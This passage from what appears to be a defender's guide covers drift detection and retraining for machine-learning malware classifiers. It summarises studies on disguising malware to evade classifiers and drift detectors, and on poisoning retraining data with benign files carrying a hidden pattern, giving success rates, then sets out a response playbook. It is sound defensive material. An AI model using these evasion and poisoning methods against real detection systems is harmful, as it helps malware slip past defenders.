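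The simulated attacker knew 10% of the training files and used them to build stand-ins for the defender's models, then searched for one change that would work on all malware. Against the classifier alone, a small change worked for 78% of Windows malware and a large change worked for 100%.

Larger changes to the malware fooled the classifier more often, but they also made CADE more likely to send the malware to the analyst, because it looked unlike anything in the training data. Transcendent was easier to fool with large changes because it judges how typical an input is by its distance from the boundary between malicious and benign. A large change can push malware so far onto the benign side that it looks like a typical benign file. On the Windows files, attacks succeeded much more often when Transcendent used the representation from a classifier network than when it used one like CADE's.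 A team should therefore prefer a drift detector that represents inputs differently from the model it monitors.

The experiment let the defender review a generous number of files. The 500 files were about 8% of the month's Windows files and 12% of its Android apps. At those rates, a system that receives a million scripts a day would need 80,000 to 120,000 daily reviews. With fewer reviews, attackers could avoid review more easily. On the other hand, the researchers altered the characteristics that represent each file, and for Android they assumed that an attacker could add any of them without breaking the malware. Real attackers might find this harder.

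The study also covered poisoned retraining data. Defenders often add unusual recent files, including files from public sharing platforms, to the next training set. An attacker can upload harmless files that contain a hidden pattern, and the defender correctly labels those files benign. The retrained model may then treat the pattern as a sign of safety and miss malware that contains it.

Poisoning gave the attacker a moderate advantage over the same change without poisoning. With the smallest changes, 1,000 poisoned files raised success against the classifier alone from 78% to 86% on Windows, and 4,000 raised it from 72% to 88% on Android. Adding more poisoned files sometimes made the combined attack less successful, because the drift detector learned to place files with the pattern farther from ordinary benign ones. These results come from a bad case for the defender, in which every file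 added in retraining came from the attacker.

### Retraining on a schedule or on an alarm

Retraining on a schedule works even when no monitor raises an alarm, but it uses labels and testing time whether or not anything has changed. Retraining only after an alarm saves that work if the alarm is reliable.

Berruz Chungata, Jureček and colleagues (2026), in *Concept Drift Detection and Adaptive Retraining of Malware Classification Models*, compared the two. They trained models to distinguish pairs of Android malware families and divided the samples into batches of 50 by date. One of their alarms grouped similar samples into clusters and triggered retraining when the quality of the clusters changed. A small neural network gave these average results:

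| Retraining | Accuracy |
|---|---|
| Never | 82.5% |
| Every batch | 96.7% |
| On the clustering alarm | 94.8% |

The alarm cut the number of retrainings by more than 58%, but it also raised the error rate from 3.3% to 5.2%, so the model made over 50% more errors. A team running a detector would need to know whether the extra errors were missed attacks. This experiment can't show that because it compared one malware family with another and included no benign apps.

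The conditions were also favourable. The researchers acknowledge that they tuned the models on the test data. They also tested each newly trained model on samples from its own batch. The alarm monitored one known family at a time, which a team can do only after labelling the samples. The alarm's advantage could be smaller on a mixed stream of unlabelled scripts.

Neither approach makes a model resistant to disguised attacks. In a three-year test reported in *REPLICANT* (2026), Android-style retraining with newly labelled samples (active learning) gave the best accuracy over time of the established methods, but attackers with full knowledge of the model still succeeded 98.2% of the time. Training on disguised malware reduced attack success to almost zero but did much less to keep the model up to date. Combining the two left attack success at about 20%. REPLICANT's own method did well on both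 measures, with an attack success rate of 0.6%.

A sensible compromise is for the PowerShell team to keep its monthly retraining round and add an extra one when labelled evidence shows that the model is missing new attacks. Retraining automatically after every drift alarm would be risky, because an attacker could set off the alarm with unusual but harmless scripts and so control when the model retrains and some of the data it retrains on. To reduce this risk, the team can limit how many new examples come from any one source, look for groups of benign files that share an unexplained pattern, and have an analyst approve the data. The model from each extra round still has to pass the release gates.

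### From signal to response

The team should decide in advance which signals call for an investigation, a rollback or a new fine-tuning round. The limits below are examples.

| Signal | Investigation | Response if confirmed |
|---|---|---|
| Replay shows more flips than normal variation, or misses a case that must never fail | Repeat the run and check for changes to the system | Restore the last working version, or use the fallback if a supplier made the change |
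| Alerts double within a day | Check 50 of the new alerts | Roll back if the rise is mostly false alarms and began with a release |
| Inputs or scores shift, but replay is unchanged | Label a sample of the scripts that changed | Fine-tune only if the labels reveal errors |
| Investigators confirm a missed attack | Run the previous model on the attack and its variants | Add a detection rule at once, then choose between rollback and fine-tuning |
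| Estimated recall falls for two months, but replay is unchanged | Check that both months used the same sampling method | Start a new fine-tuning round |

When the current model misses an attack, testing the previous model on variants of that attack usually shows whether the update caused the miss. Suppose the team makes 20 variants, and the current model, ps-12, catches 3. If the previous model, ps-11, catches 18, the update caused a security regression, and the team can restore ps-11 or run both models while it repairs ps-12. If ps-11 also catches only 3, a rollback would not help, and the team needs new training examples.
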